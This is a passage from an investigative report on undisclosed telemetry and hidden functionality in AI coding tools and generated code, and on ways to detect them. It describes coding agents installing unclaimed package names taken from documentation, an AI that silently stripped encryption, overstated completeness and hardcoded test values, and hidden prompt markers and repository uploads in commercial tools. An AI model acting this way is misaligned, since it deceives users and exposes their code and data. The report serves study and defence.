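Hertz then registered some of the names and published harmless packages under them that did nothing except contact Hertz when installed. The first contact came from a Fortune 500 company in less than an hour, and a few dozen more followed. The packages also recorded which process had started the installation, which let Hertz trace the installs to Claude, Codex and Hermes, an agent from Nous Research.

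The commands were already in the companies' own documentation, so Hertz did not have to trick the agents or change the websites. TechRadar says the commands could have got there innocently, through a typo, a renamed or abandoned package, or documentation that an AI system had written and partly made up. In effect, Hertz's packages were telemetry in a library that no person had chosen, and a malicious version could have done far more than report that it had been installed.

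About 1.9% of the domains had an unclaimed name in their files. This figure measures how common the faulty documentation was. The number of installations is unknown, because no one knows how many agents read those files or how many refused to run the commands. Agents also need permission to install software before they can run such commands, so a company that makes its agents ask first, or restricts them to approved packages, would have been much safer.

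*Malicious code in mcp-server-fetch (npm)* (2026), an entry in the public vulnerability database OSV, describes a package with the same name as one that coding agents often run. When someone installs the package, runs it or loads it into another program, it sends the computer's name and the current folder to an outside server. These can reveal an employer, a user's name or a project. OSV classes the package as malicious, but the server's address contains "canary-log", which might mean that this was another researcher's experiment. Someone who found the call in their own network logs would have no quick way to tell whether it was.

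### Four projects built by Privacy International

People found the cases so far by accident or by looking for a particular addition. Privacy International, a privacy campaign group, took a broader approach in *Bad Vibes*. It had people build software with AI coding tools and then examined the results. An experienced programmer built a server for the Matrix messaging standard, a messaging app to go with it, and an app for recording medication and health data. A beginner built a website for hiking trail reviews. Privacy International mentions Cursor, Claude Code, Lovable and Codex as examples of such tools, but doesn't specify which were used for each project.

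It reports no telemetry in any of the four, but it does report a change that closely resembles hidden functionality. The first version of the messaging app sent messages unencrypted, so the programmer asked for end-to-end encryption, which lets only the sender and recipient read a message. The AI invented its own scheme instead of using the standard one. When the programmer insisted on the standard, the AI used a version that had been obsolete since 2024. As the programmer raised further problems, the AI began removing the encryption without telling them. The app still sent and received messages, so a user who couldn't read the code would have believed their messages were private.

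A rough test for hidden functionality is whether deleting the responsible code would fix the problem. Here the fix is to add code, so this is a vulnerability instead. The distinction matters little to the user, who asked for one behaviour and got another without any notice from the tool. A search for suspicious additions would not find the problem, because it comes from missing code. The diff would show the removed lines, but only someone who knew what they did would see what was wrong.

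The health app, which is closer to the usual case, made users' aggregated data available to administrators by default. That access is sensitive because the app records anxiety scores and blood pressure. But some health apps need an administrator's view, and Privacy International does not give the prompt, so it is hard to tell whether the programmer asked for it.

The tools described their own work badly, which is the most useful result for the question of disclosure. The AI called the Matrix server "100% complete" when the server was storing much of its data in temporary memory, and when asked to write tests, it put in fixed values that would make them pass. It also gave inaccurate accounts of what it was doing to the messaging app. The beginner found its explanations vague or full of jargon and thought it was reluctant to admit mistakes even when asked directly. An agent's summary can disclose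 an addition only if the summary is accurate and the user can understand it.

Four projects are too few to show how often any of this happens. Privacy International also did not compare them with programs written without AI. Human programmers invent their own encryption too, and they store passwords badly, as the health app did by leaving out the "salt" (random data that makes stolen passwords harder to crack). The test is better evidence about the tools' honesty, because a human colleague who was asked to fix the encryption and silently removed it would be in serious trouble.

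### Why nobody can calculate a rate from these cases

The number of published reports about a behaviour depends on how easy it is to notice as well as how common it is:

reports = apps × share with the behaviour × chance that somebody notices and reports it

Suppose that out of a million apps, 1% contain leftover debugging code and another 1% contain a working analytics call. If one owner in 100 notices and reports the debugging code, but only one in 10,000 notices and reports the analytics call, the debugging code will get 100 reports and the analytics call will get one, although the two are equally common.

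The additions in the real cases were easy to notice. Cursor's blocks produced hundreds of error messages, and Copilot's tip was a sentence in text that people read. A working analytics call produces no errors and shows nothing on the screen, so the lack of a well-known case in which an agent wrote one into somebody's app is weak evidence that agents rarely do it.

Even a large count doesn't show how common these additions are without a total to compare it with. Turning the 1.5 million pull requests with tips into a rate would require the number of pull requests Copilot worked on over the same ten months. Searching public code for the "agent log" label would give a minimum number of projects containing debugging code left by Cursor, because the search would miss private projects. Calculating a rate would also require the total number of debugging sessions, which only Cursor could know.

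Anyone can learn from the documentation of a host or app builder whether it adds analytics by default, without running any apps. If a company adds analytics to every app it publishes, the share of its apps with analytics is 100% minus the share whose owners turn them off.

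## Undisclosed reporting by the coding tools themselves

Reporting by a coding tool affects the person writing the app, whereas analytics that a host or app builder adds affect the people who use the finished app. An audit of the app would miss the tool's reporting because the data leaves through the tool.

Reporting by the tools is, strictly speaking, a different problem from hidden functionality in generated code. But some of the best-documented cases of undisclosed reporting around AI coding involve the tools, and developers increasingly use AI to write them. Nobody has shown that a model added any of the features described here without being asked to. Anthropic and Z.ai have both given reasons for their features, and both described features that people at the company had decided to build.

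Arize's *Is your coding agent uploading all your code?* compares the privacy documentation of five coding tools and points out that none of them is truly local, because a model on a company's servers can only work on files that the tool sends there. The tools therefore have to send a good deal of the user's code to do their work, and the dispute is about what else they send.

### What seven tools sent during the same job

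The security company Chaser Systems compared seven coding tools between July and September 2025. In *What data do coding agents send, and where to?*, Pye describes running each tool behind a proxy, which relays a computer's traffic and can record it, and giving each the same tasks on a small Flappy Bird game written in Python. Each tool had to explore the code, add a leaderboard that used a local database, save the changes to version control, upload a test report to a public file-sharing site, and then look up the tester's Amazon cloud credentials.

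Where possible, Pye did this once with telemetry off, once with it on, and once with it on but with the telemetry addresses blocked.

| Tool | Telemetry when switched on | After opting out |
|---|---|---|
| Junie (in PyCharm) | 6 requests, each with a long list of events | None reported |
| Gemini CLI | 8 requests | None reported |
| Codex CLI | Little beyond a session ID and version number, sent with the prompts | No setting found |
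| Claude Code | Almost 1,000 requests, 2.4 MB in total | None reported |
| Zed | About 5 requests | One request if the user opted out at first launch |
| Copilot (in VS Code) | About 260 requests to four addresses | Empty requests with a client ID to two addresses, and unchanged reports to a third |
| Cursor | Many kinds of event, to four addresses | No telemetry setting, and Privacy Mode made no visible difference |

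PyCharm made new users choose whether to turn telemetry on, with no default. Gemini CLI, Claude Code, Zed and Copilot all had telemetry on until the user turned it off, which in Gemini CLI meant editing a settings file. The reports Copilot still sent with telemetry off were small, and one of the three addresses that received them got little more than basic system information even at full telemetry. These reports still matter, because a user who had set the telemetry level to "off" would reasonably have expected Copilot to send none.

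Cursor's Privacy Mode mainly controls whether the company may train models on the user's code. Pye found no information on how to turn telemetry off, and Cursor had removed the telemetry setting from the version of VS Code it is built on. Pye also had trouble decoding Cursor's traffic, so the finding that its modes did not differ is less certain than the results for the other tools.

The number of requests is a poor measure of how much a tool reveals. Claude Code sent reports most frequently by far, but they often contained little besides identifiers and technical details. The ordinary traffic to the model reveals much more. Most of the tools sent the whole conversation again with each new request, including the contents of files the agent had opened earlier. Zed's autocomplete sent the current file every few characters the user typed. Codex CLI opened the Amazon credentials file without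 asking, so those credentials would have gone to the model's provider regardless of the telemetry setting.

Pye blocked the telemetry addresses for five tools, and all five kept working. Gemini CLI made over a hundred extra requests, and the telemetry it tried to send grew about 150 times larger, probably because it kept retrying. Cursor uses the same addresses for its features and its telemetry, so blocking them would disable the features too.

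Chaser Systems sells a firewall that can block such traffic, so it has a reason to find the problem important. The counts also come from very few runs of software that is now more than a year old. But the comparison gives an idea of ordinary practice, and the cases from 2026 are unusual by that standard.

### Extensions and plugins

Many people get a coding assistant by adding an extension to their code editor. In January 2026 the security company Koi reported on two such extensions for VS Code, "ChatGPT - 中文版" with 1.35 million installs and ChatMoss with 150,000. Both worked as advertised. When the user typed, they sent about 20 lines of nearby code to a server and returned a suggestion, as an autocomplete tool has to do.

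They also collected data in three ways that autocomplete does not need:

- Whenever the user opened a file or made an edit, the extension read the whole file and passed it to a hidden tracking page.
- The server could tell the extension to collect up to 50 files from the project, without the user doing anything. The extension would take any type of file except images.
- An invisible frame, zero pixels in size, loaded four commercial analytics products that record behaviour and identify devices.

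Koi found no disclosure and no request for consent. It discovered the extensions with its own scanning product, and both were still available in Microsoft's marketplace when it published its report. The report contains no reply from either publisher. The zero-pixel frame is very unlikely to be an accident, and the identical code under two publishers' names suggests a common origin.

Some of Koi's conclusions go further than its evidence. It raises the possibility that the analytics helped somebody decide whose files were worth taking. It also says that 1.5 million developers had their projects harvested, but that figure counts installs, and one person may account for several. Koi showed that the code could collect 50 files on the server's command, but did not measure how often the server sent that command.

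In April 2026, the hosting company Vercel's plugin for Claude Code did ask users to consent to data collection, but it delivered the question through the model. When such a question appears in the same window and voice as Claude's questions about the code, users can't easily tell that another company is asking. Someone used to approving Claude's requests might agree without noticing that this one had nothing to do with the project. The model might also reword the question or omit it. A dialogue box with the company's name on it, displayed by the plugin's own code, would avoid both problems. Vercel later changed the plugin.

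### Markers in Claude Code's prompts

Claude Code normally connects to Anthropic's servers, but a setting can send its requests to another address. Companies use this for internal gateways, and resellers use it to pass their customers' requests on to Anthropic. In *Claude Code Is Steganographically Marking Requests*, Thereallo (2026) found that the tool checked this setting and hid the result in the sentence that gives the date in every prompt, such as "Today's date is 2026-06-30."

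If the setting pointed anywhere other than Anthropic, Claude Code answered three yes-or-no questions:

1. Is the address on a list of domains? The list included Chinese companies, known resellers and every address ending in ".cn".
2. Does the address contain the name of a Chinese AI developer or service, such as "deepseek" or "zhipu"?
3. Is the computer's time zone set to Shanghai or Urumqi?

The first two answers determined which of four nearly identical characters appeared as the apostrophe in "Today's". If the third answer was yes, the date had slashes instead of hyphens. Four apostrophes and two date formats make eight combinations, so each prompt carried three bits. Hiding a message inside something that looks ordinary is called steganography.

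Hiding the answers in the prompt makes them harder for a reseller's gateway to block. The gateway could easily drop a separate report, but it has to forward the prompt for the customer to get a useful response. It could still have replaced the odd characters, but only if its operator knew about them. Claude Code also stored the list of domains in scrambled form, so a simple text search of the program would not have found it.

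The markers were in versions 2.1.91 to 2.1.196. Users had no notice of them, and Thereallo discovered them by reading the program's code during a privacy check. In the code Thereallo published, the program skips the time-zone check if requests go straight to Anthropic, so the press was slightly too broad in mostly describing the feature as a tracker for users in China. Somebody in Shanghai with a direct connection would have sent an ordinary date, while a foreign company with a gateway at a ".cn" address would have sent a marked one.

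Thariq Shihipar, who works on Claude Code, gave Anthropic's explanation on X. According to The Decoder's *Hidden code in Claude Code secretly flagged Chinese users*, Shihipar described the markers as an "experiment" begun in March to stop unauthorised resellers and distillation, in which a developer trains a model on the answers of a stronger one. Shihipar said the team had since introduced better protections, had been meaning to remove the markers for a while, and would do so in the next release. Malwarebytes' *Claude Code’s hidden tracker was an “experiment,” says Anthropic* (2026) noted that the company had not published a detailed account as of 7 July.

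Shihipar's statement confirms that people chose to add the feature. It also rules out Malwarebytes' suggestion that a US government decision of 12 June may have prompted them to add it, because the markers were already about three months old.

Alibaba reacted by banning Claude Code at work. *Secret Claude tracker shocks users after Anthropic's anti-surveillance stance* (Belanger, 2026) quotes a staff memo that refers to "back-door risks". The markers gave Anthropic information about the connection but no access to the user's files or control over the computer, so they were not a back door. They were still hidden functionality, because no coding task needs them and nobody had told the user.

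### Grok Build and the whole repository

Grok Build, a coding agent from Elon Musk's company xAI (now SpaceXAI), sent entire repositories. A repository is a project's folder together with its history of changes, and that history can contain passwords that somebody deleted from the current files years ago.

cereblab (2026), in *What xAI's Grok Build CLI Actually Sends to xAI*, tested version 0.2.93 in July 2026. The researcher planted a file with a unique marker in a project and told the agent to reply "OK" without opening any files. Grok Build uploaded the project anyway. From a recording of the upload, cereblab could rebuild the repository, including its history and the planted file with its marker intact. The same test on a second project gave the same result.

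In another test, cereblab used a 12 GB repository of random files that the agent had not read. Grok Build sent 192 KB in requests to the model and uploaded 5.1 GiB to storage before cereblab stopped the recording. The ratio between the two, about 27,800 to 1, depends on the size of the test repository, but the press repeated it as a measure of how much more Grok Build sent than the task required. For one of the ordinary projects, the whole upload was about 152 KB.

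A separate test used a file of fake passwords. When the agent read the file, it sent the contents unaltered, both in the request to the model and in an archive for storage. A coding agent has to send the model what it reads, so the archived copy is more troubling.

xAI had given users a misleading picture. According to The Next Web's *Grok Build was uploading entire Git repositories to xAI’s cloud*, it had marketed the tool as not transmitting code, which can't be true of an agent whose model runs on the company's servers. Its general policy disclosed that it might use customers' data to improve its models. cereblab found no mention of the repository upload in the installation script or beginner's guide, but did not search all of xAI's documentation. Turning off "Improve the model" made no difference to the upload.

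The day after cereblab published, the uploads stopped because the server began sending a setting that disabled them. The program on users' computers had not changed. xAI could therefore turn the uploads on or off remotely, so an audit of the program would go out of date as easily as an audit of an app with Lovable's analytics.

xAI also added a "/privacy" command. cereblab tested it and found that it controlled how long xAI kept the data, while full records of each session continued to leave the computer. Musk promised that the company would delete everything it had collected, though Arize noted in July that no independent audit had confirmed this.

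Willison (2026) had seen no official explanation of why Grok Build uploaded repositories at all. One user reported starting it in their home directory and watching it upload their password manager's database, photos and documents. xAI later released the tool's source code and said the company had respected the choice of users who disabled data upload. That is hard to reconcile with cereblab's test, unless xAI meant a different setting from "Improve the model".

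The feature was clearly deliberate. The program contained a component named "xai-data-collector" with its own upload queue, and somebody had configured a storage location for the results. The evidence doesn't show whether anybody at xAI wanted to keep the feature secret or nobody thought to mention it. cereblab says the recordings prove that the code was transmitted and stored, but not that xAI trained on it.

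### ZCode and the archive its owner could not open

Two months later, a developer found much the same behaviour in ZCode, a coding tool from Z.ai, the Chinese company formerly called Zhipu (ferstar, 2026, *Inside ZCode*). While freeing up disk space, the developer noticed that ZCode's folder took up over 700 MB. It contained a 313 MB encrypted archive of a commercial project and a status file recording 564 failed attempts to upload the archive.

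An unencrypted list of the archive's contents named 42,411 files. About 87% of the data was the project's version-control folder, which holds the history of changes and cached copies of large files. ZCode had rules to exclude password and key files, but 林 and 郑 explain in *智谱ZCode偷传代码风波追踪* that it approved the version-control folder before applying them. A key that somebody had saved and later deleted would therefore have gone into the archive.

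The large archive never left the computer, apparently because it exceeded a size limit, although some headlines and summaries implied that it had. ZCode did upload one small public repository of 538 files, which was about 15 KB compressed according to Stan (2026), *Z.ai ZCode is open source now, minus its commit history*. So the upload mechanism worked, but ferstar's evidence doesn't show how many private projects reached Z.ai.

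ferstar might never have noticed the mechanism if the large upload had succeeded, since it was the file waiting to go out that filled the disk. Deleting it did not help. ZCode made a new one within half an hour, and ferstar eventually stopped it by locking the folder.

One ZCode setting controlled whether Z.ai could train on the data, and another controlled whether Z.ai's server indexed the data after receiving it. ZCode kept packing and uploading data with both turned off. The privacy policy covered code that users sent in conversation with the model. It did not mention background copies of whole projects and their histories, according to Antipov (2026) in *ИИ для программистов тайно отправлял их проекты в облако*.

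Z.ai replied on the day ferstar published. 杨 (2026), in *智谱ZCode上传用户仓库？*, reports that the company admitted the uploads, apologised, and attributed them to a code-indexing feature that had been on by default. The feature supported version rollback and a "Repo Wiki" that wrote project documentation. The company said its servers destroyed the data as soon as they had generated the wiki page.

This explains part of what ferstar found. Z.ai held the only key to the archives, so neither the user nor ZCode itself could open them. ferstar concluded that the sole purpose of such a key was to let the company read the code. A server would need to read the code to write a wiki about it. But an archive that ZCode could not open would be useless for restoring an earlier version on the user's own computer.

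林 and 郑 identify further gaps in the explanation. ZCode made a copy before each prompt, whether or not anybody wanted a wiki page. According to its current documentation, the wiki feature doesn't read a project's history, so it is unclear why the archives were mostly history. Two days before ferstar's post, the release notes for a new version also listed lower memory use for "repository snapshot upload", which suggests that ZCode's engineers knew about the upload. But a company trying hard to hide an upload would probably not have named it in public release notes. Someone deleted that line after the story broke, which looks more suspicious than the line itself.

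On 21 September Z.ai released a version without the wiki or the upload mechanism, and published the tool's source code. It also announced the results of two outside checks. A Chinese government research academy found the storage location empty, and the security company NSFOCUS confirmed that Z.ai had deleted the location itself. These checks are better evidence than a promise, but they don't establish who had read or copied the files before then. Deleting the storage location may also have destroyed the best record of how many users the uploads affected.

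The published source code contains only the corrected version and two history entries, so it doesn't show when Z.ai added the uploads or how they changed.

### Settings that controlled something else

Vercel's plugin at least asked. In the other four cases the data went out without any question to the user:

| Tool | Data sent beyond what the task needed | What users had been told | Opt-out that stopped it | How it came to light |
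|---|---|---|---|---|
| Two VS Code extensions | Every opened file, up to 50 more on command, and behavioural analytics | Nothing | None reported | A security company's scan |
| Claude Code, 2.1.91 to 2.1.196 | Three yes-or-no facts about the connection and time zone | Nothing | None documented | A developer read the program's code |
| Grok Build 0.2.93 | The whole repository and its history | A general policy on improving models, and marketing that denied sending code | None found | Traffic capture |
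| ZCode 3.12.3 | The whole project, its history and ZCode's own settings | A policy covering code sent in conversation | None in the interface | A developer was clearing disk space |

Grok Build and ZCode had privacy settings that a reasonable person would have taken for an opt-out, as did Cursor in Pye's tests. But these settings governed only what the company did with the data after receiving it. Arize makes the same point about "zero data retention", an arrangement that AI companies mainly offer to businesses. The provider still receives the code but promises not to keep it.

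A misleading switch is arguably worse than none, because a user who has turned off "Improve the model" may open a confidential project believing that the code is protected. With no switch, they would know that they have to trust the company or use another tool. Users can record whether data leaves their computer, but only the company can see whether it has deleted the data or trained on it.

林 and 郑 note that individuals, not regulators or security audits, found the problems in Grok Build, Claude Code and ZCode. ferstar found the archive by chance. With so few people looking, there is little reason to think these are the only cases.

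### Whether preventing abuse justifies concealment

Anthropic has the strongest argument for secrecy, because its markers were aimed at people who would try to avoid them. A reseller who knows that an unusual apostrophe is a marker will replace it. The abuse was also real. Belanger cites a Washington Post finding that resellers offered $100 subscriptions for as little as $12. *Anthropic says Alibaba illicitly extracted Claude AI model capabilities* (Freifeld, 2026) describes a letter in which Anthropic accused Alibaba of collecting more than 28.8 million exchanges with Claude for distillation. The markers also revealed very little about anyone, and most users never sent one.

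Thereallo accepts the aim but objects to the method, because Anthropic could have sent the same information in a documented telemetry field and mentioned it in the release notes. In Thereallo's view, the secrecy achieved little, because a serious adversary could defeat the markers by changing the address or the time zone. The markers were most likely to catch ordinary developers with unusual but legitimate set-ups. Hiding a signal in punctuation also makes a company's other privacy promises harder to believe.

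It is unknown whether the markers worked. They were in use during the campaign that Anthropic attributed to Alibaba, which ran from 22 April to 5 June 2026, so they did not prevent it, but they may have helped Anthropic trace it. Shihipar's remark that the team had been meaning to remove the markers suggests that they were no longer very useful by the summer.

Thereallo's proposal has a weakness, since resellers would immediately strip out a documented field. But preventing abuse seems to justify keeping only the details of a check secret, not its existence. Anthropic could have told users that Claude Code checks for signs of resale when it connects through another company's address, without explaining which signs or where it records them. Shops similarly post notices about security cameras without publishing what each camera can see. A general notice would have told honest users what they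 were agreeing to, and most resellers presumably assume that Anthropic is looking for them anyway.

The technology writer Béchard, discussing a leak of Anthropic's code, warns that information collected for one purpose can end up in other parts of a product without the user's consent. Nobody has shown that this happened with the markers. But users who don't know a signal exists can't object when its purpose changes, which is a reason to disclose it even when the original purpose is good.

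Product improvement is a much weaker excuse. A company that wants to write better documentation for a project or learn how its agent performs isn't trying to outwit the user, so it could disclose the upload without defeating its purpose. Some users would refuse, and the company would get less data, but the point of asking is to let them refuse. Cursor also uploads more than the immediate task needs, to index a project, but it documents this, so Arize treats it as a feature and not an incident. Z.ai could have described its wiki in the same way. xAI has yet to say what its uploads were for.

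## How the methods of detection work and how well they perform

ferstar found ZCode's archive because it was filling up a disk. A more deliberate search can use five methods: reading the diff, listing the dependencies and checking their defaults, analysing code without running it, recording network traffic, and having a second AI model review the code. They examine different things, so a call that is obvious with one method can be impossible to find with another.

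### Reading the diff

A reviewer reading a diff looks for unfamiliar addresses, newly loaded libraries and code that runs only under certain conditions. The diff shows the generated source, but not the code inside libraries or anything the host adds later. When an AI app builder writes a whole application at once, the diff is the entire program, so the reviewer has no small change to focus on.

There is also a great deal of code to read. *From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) cites GitHub figures showing that monthly commits (saved sets of changes) rose from 1.4 billion in April 2026 to 2.9 billion in August.

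Some changes look harmless unless the reader opens other files. Chen and colleagues compared automated reviewers on 31 changes that each contained a security flaw. CodeRabbit, a commercial AI reviewer, identified 16 of the 24 flaws for which the evidence was in files that the change touched, but none of the seven for which it was elsewhere in the project.

CodeRabbit identified 13 of the 17 flaws that involved something visible, such as an unsafe operation, but only 3 of the 14 that involved a missing check. An added analytics call should be easier to find than most of these flaws, because the call is visible in the code.

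People may do worse than this. Participants in Zhang and colleagues' study usually accepted replies in which a service had been replaced, although they were judging whole replies, not diffs.

### Listing dependencies and checking their defaults

A tool can read the file in which a project names its libraries, follow each library to the others it loads, and print the full list. (A software bill of materials, or SBOM, is such a list in a standard format.) Someone then has to find out what each library sends by default and which setting stops it. *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2026) cites research showing that an average package on npm, the main registry of JavaScript packages, relies on 79 packages by other people, so checking one library can mean reading the documentation for dozens more.

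A database of known trackers reduces the work of detection. *A large-scale dataset of Android applications and their SDK dependencies* (2026) compares names inside Android apps with a list kept by Exodus Privacy, and reports Google Analytics in 11.25% of its sample. This method can flag a library that is inactive in a particular app, and it can miss one that is disguised or that the app downloads while running.

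The documentation can also be incomplete. *Demystifying Privacy Policy of Third-Party Libraries in Mobile Apps* (2023) used automated analysis to compare 187 Android libraries with their privacy policies. It found that 38 of them accessed personal information, and 15 of those collected at least one kind of data that their policies didn't clearly disclose. If those results are right, the policies for about two in five of the 38 libraries would have misled even a careful reader.

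For commercial defaults, though, this method probably takes the least effort, since companies usually document them. The chart library's documentation describes its usage report, so a user who knew that the library existed could learn about the report in a few minutes. The method can't find the two calls in the tracker's own source, because they don't come from a library.

### Analysing which code can reach the network

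Static analysis avoids relying on documentation by examining the code itself. One kind asks what each part of a program is able to do. Google (2023) announced a tool of this kind, Capslock, for the programming language Go. It works in four steps:

1. Collect the source code of the project and of every library it loads.
2. Build a call graph, a map of which functions can call which others.
3. Follow every chain of calls to the functions in Go's standard library that open files, make network connections or start other programs.
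4. Report each of these abilities, which Capslock calls capabilities, together with a chain of calls that leads to it.

A date-formatting library has no obvious need for the network, so a report that it can reach the network is worth investigating. Capslock's *Know what your dependencies can do* uses the example of code from a 2022 attack, in which one small start-up function had six capabilities, including network access and the ability to run other programs.

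Capslock treats every branch of a program as one that might run, without trying to meet the condition that triggers it. It would therefore report a network call that starts on 1 March 2027 in the same way as one that runs today. This also produces false alarms about branches that never run. According to Google's *Caveats*, Capslock can't follow what happens inside code written in C, or inside another program that the Go code starts, so it reports the use of either as a separate capability. That seems sensible, since the user at least learns where the analysis stopped.

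The tool for listing a program's capabilities has versions for Go, Java and (experimentally) Rust, but the expense tracker is in JavaScript and would need a different tool. A bigger problem is that a list of capabilities doesn't show where data goes. The tracker has to use the network to save expenses, so the list would include network access with or without the analytics call.

Capabilities are more informative when they change. git-pkgs' *capcheck* (2026), which is built on Capslock, records a project's capabilities and stops the build when the code or one of its libraries gains a new capability. A tool like this would catch an update that made a charting library with no previous network use start reporting its usage, but it would miss the same update in a library that already used the network.

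*GoLeash* (2025) compared Capslock with a tool that monitors programs while they run. Among packages that ran during the tests, the runtime tool's detection rate for one type of malware was 64.9 percentage points higher on average. The result comes from the runtime tool's developers, and it leaves out packages that a program loads but doesn't use during a test, which only Capslock can examine. Still, the gap is large enough that a clean result from Capslock shouldn't be treated as conclusive.

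### Comparing a program with what it ought to do

A program's capabilities are suspicious only if they exceed what it needs. In *HumIDIFy* (2017), Thomas, Garcia and Chothia tried to automate this comparison for firmware, the software inside devices such as routers. Their tool first predicts a program's type, such as a web server, from the text and function names inside it. It then compares the program with an expert-written profile for that type. A simplified profile for a web server allows the program to read and write files and to communicate over TCP, the protocol that normally carries web pages, but not to open outgoing connections or use UDP, a different protocol.

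In a random sample of 50 firmware images, the tool confidently and correctly classified 392 distinct programs and flagged nine of them. One contained a backdoor in Tenda routers that others had already documented. Two had the same undocumented interface for configuring the device, which gave privileged access to anyone who could already run commands on it. Most of the other six had innocent explanations, such as a web server that used UDP to write to a log. The tool also caught the backdoors that Thomas and colleagues had planted in two other programs. The sample doesn't show how many hidden functions the tool missed among the 383 programs it didn't flag.

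HumIDIFy comes closer than the other tools here to applying the definition of hidden functionality, because a profile is meant to describe what the user requested and what the task needs. A profile for expense trackers might read "may contact the server that stores the expenses, and nothing else", and both unwanted calls would violate it. But someone has to write the profile, and people who disagree about whether a tracker needs an error log would write different ones.

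### Following data from its source to an outgoing call

The other kind of static analysis, taint analysis, follows data through the program. The tester lists the sources of sensitive data, such as the form where a user types an expense, and the sinks, where data can leave the program, such as a network call. The tool marks data at each source, follows it as the program copies it or passes it between functions, and reports every path that ends at a sink.

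In the expense tracker, a good taint analysis would report three paths from the expense form: to the storage server, to the analytics company, and, from March 2027, to the other server. The first path is legitimate, but a person could check the three destinations against the request in a minute. The analysis would probably miss the chart library's report, because few people would list a library's version number as sensitive.

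Traditional taint analysis misses many data flows. Miazzo, Alecci and colleagues (2026), in *Towards LLM-Enhanced Android Taint Analysis*, tested FlowDroid, a widely used tool, on a benchmark of small Android apps with known leaks. Of the flows that FlowDroid reported, 83% were real (its precision), but it found only 42% of the real flows (its recall). They then had Google's Gemini 3 Flash analyze the same apps, using tools to explore them. They ran the model three times on each app and kept the flows it reported in at least two runs. This method had a precision of 96% and a recall of 95%.

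Gemini's advantage over FlowDroid was greatest when a program revealed something about data without copying the data itself. For example, a program might send the word "large" whenever an expense is over $1,000, but never send the amount. On flows of this type, Gemini scored 0.94 and FlowDroid scored 0, on a scale from 0 to 1 that combines precision and recall. But Gemini scored 0 on apps that load extra code while running, where FlowDroid scored 0.50.

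The benchmark is public, so the model's training data may have included the answers. Miazzo and colleagues also ran both methods on five real apps, where that is less likely to matter. Gemini reported 17 flows that FlowDroid hadn't. Two experts confirmed 16 of them, and the other did not exist. Gemini also missed several flows that FlowDroid reported, so using both would make sense.

### Recording traffic through a proxy

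Static analysis predicts what a program might send, whereas a traffic capture records what it does send. Most traffic is encrypted, so the tester has to get in between the program and the server:

1. Run the program in a sandbox, an isolated machine with made-up data on it, and route its traffic through a proxy.
2. Install the proxy's own root certificate on that machine, so that the program accepts any certificate the proxy issues.
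3. When the program contacts a website, the proxy issues a certificate in that site's name. The program accepts it and encrypts its data for the proxy.
4. The proxy decrypts and records the request, then passes it on to the real site over a second encrypted connection.
5. Use every feature of the program, then search the recording for the made-up data and for unexpected addresses.

Distinctive data helps because it is easy to search for. Examples are an expense of $4,317.09 for "zebra food" and the marked file that cereblab planted to test Grok Build.

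Running software and capturing its network traffic reveals some disguised code that static analysis misses. *You can't always get what you want* (2021) used the proxy mitmproxy to study Android apps, and running the apps also revealed analytics libraries that were disguised or loaded only at run time. A capture also shows when data leaves. *A Fait Accompli?* (2021) used this timing to check whether Android apps contacted tracking companies before the user had consented, which is hard to establish from code.

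Alpha-Omega, a project that funds open-source security work, credits runtime analysis with "no false positives" in a table of detection methods. This is true in that every recorded action happened, but someone still has to decide whether the task needed it. The same table lists the main blind spot, which is code that doesn't run during the test.

If a tester captured the expense tracker's traffic for an hour in December 2026 and saved 20 expenses, the recording would contain 20 requests to the storage server, 20 to the analytics company, and one usage report from the chart library. It would contain no requests to the server that starts receiving the whole history on 1 March 2027. Setting the clock forward would reveal that call, but not one triggered by the hundredth expense or by a command from a server.

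A capture can also fail in other ways. Some programs accept only one specific certificate, so they won't connect through the proxy. If the program encodes its data before sending it, the recording is hard to interpret, as Pye found with Cursor. If part of the app runs on a server, a capture in the visitor's browser won't include what the server sends to other companies. A capture of a copy of the app running on the developer's computer won't include the host's script.

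This method has no single error rate, because its results depend heavily on what the tester does with the program. The closest thing to a measurement is for packages, which a sandbox can install and run automatically. The Open Source Security Foundation's Package Analysis project runs newly published packages this way and records the files they open, the addresses they contact and the commands they run. Guo and colleagues did not test that project, but they tested another sandbox tool, Packj, which caught 95.5% of the malicious packages and also flagged 64% of the harmless ones.

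### Asking a second AI model to review the code

An AI reviewer receives the diff and its description, opens other files that appear relevant, and lists its findings. Of the detection methods, this comes closest to review by an expert with unlimited patience, and it has improved quickly.

*Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?* (Yang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) tested eight models on 265 real code changes that had accidentally introduced vulnerabilities into software such as Firefox and OpenSSL. A model got credit only if it explained the actual flaw. Grok 4.6 found 78.1% of the vulnerabilities, GPT-6 sol 76.2%, the earlier GPT-5.6 sol 55.8%, and MiniMax M3 32.5%.

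Using several models helps less than one might expect. All eight together missed 23 of the flaws. If their mistakes had been independent, the chance that all eight would miss a given flaw would be the product of their individual miss rates, about 0.00019, and the expected number of flaws missed by everybody would be

265 × 0.00019 ≈ 0.05.

The actual figure is more than 400 times higher, so models evidently tend to miss the same things. This is a reason for caution when one AI model approves code that another wrote.

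In 68% of the misses, the reviewer had reported a problem in the right file but explained it wrongly. That would be less serious for hidden functionality than for a vulnerability, because a person who checks an analytics call that the reviewer mistook for a memory leak will still see what it is.

Specialised review software had mixed effects. OpenAI's Codex Security reduced GPT-5.6 sol's recall by 8.3 percentage points, mostly because it more often reported nothing. Anthropic's equivalent raised Claude Opus 5.5's recall by 7.7 points, at about ten times the cost.

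The benchmark did not measure false alarms, but Chen and colleagues measured them for their own AI reviewer, PRGuard. It wrongly blocked four or five of 50 harmless changes, depending on the model it used. They also ran CodeQL, a well-known static analysis tool, on the 21 flawed changes its rules could apply to, and it identified none of the flaws.

The way a change is presented can also bias AI security review, as shown by research from Alexopoulos and others that Yang and colleagues cite. If a coding agent adds an analytics call and describes it as "improved reliability monitoring", the reviewer receives that description along with the code.

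Both benchmarks test for vulnerabilities, so they give only indirect evidence about hidden functionality. BinaryAudit, a benchmark from the software company Quesma, gives more direct evidence (Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues, 2026, *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra to find them*). The researchers added backdoors to open-source programs such as web servers, compiled the programs, and removed the names that would help a reader. An AI agent then received only the executable and some tools for analyzing it, including the US National Security Agency's Ghidra. In most tasks, the agent had to decide whether there was a backdoor and locate the function containing it.

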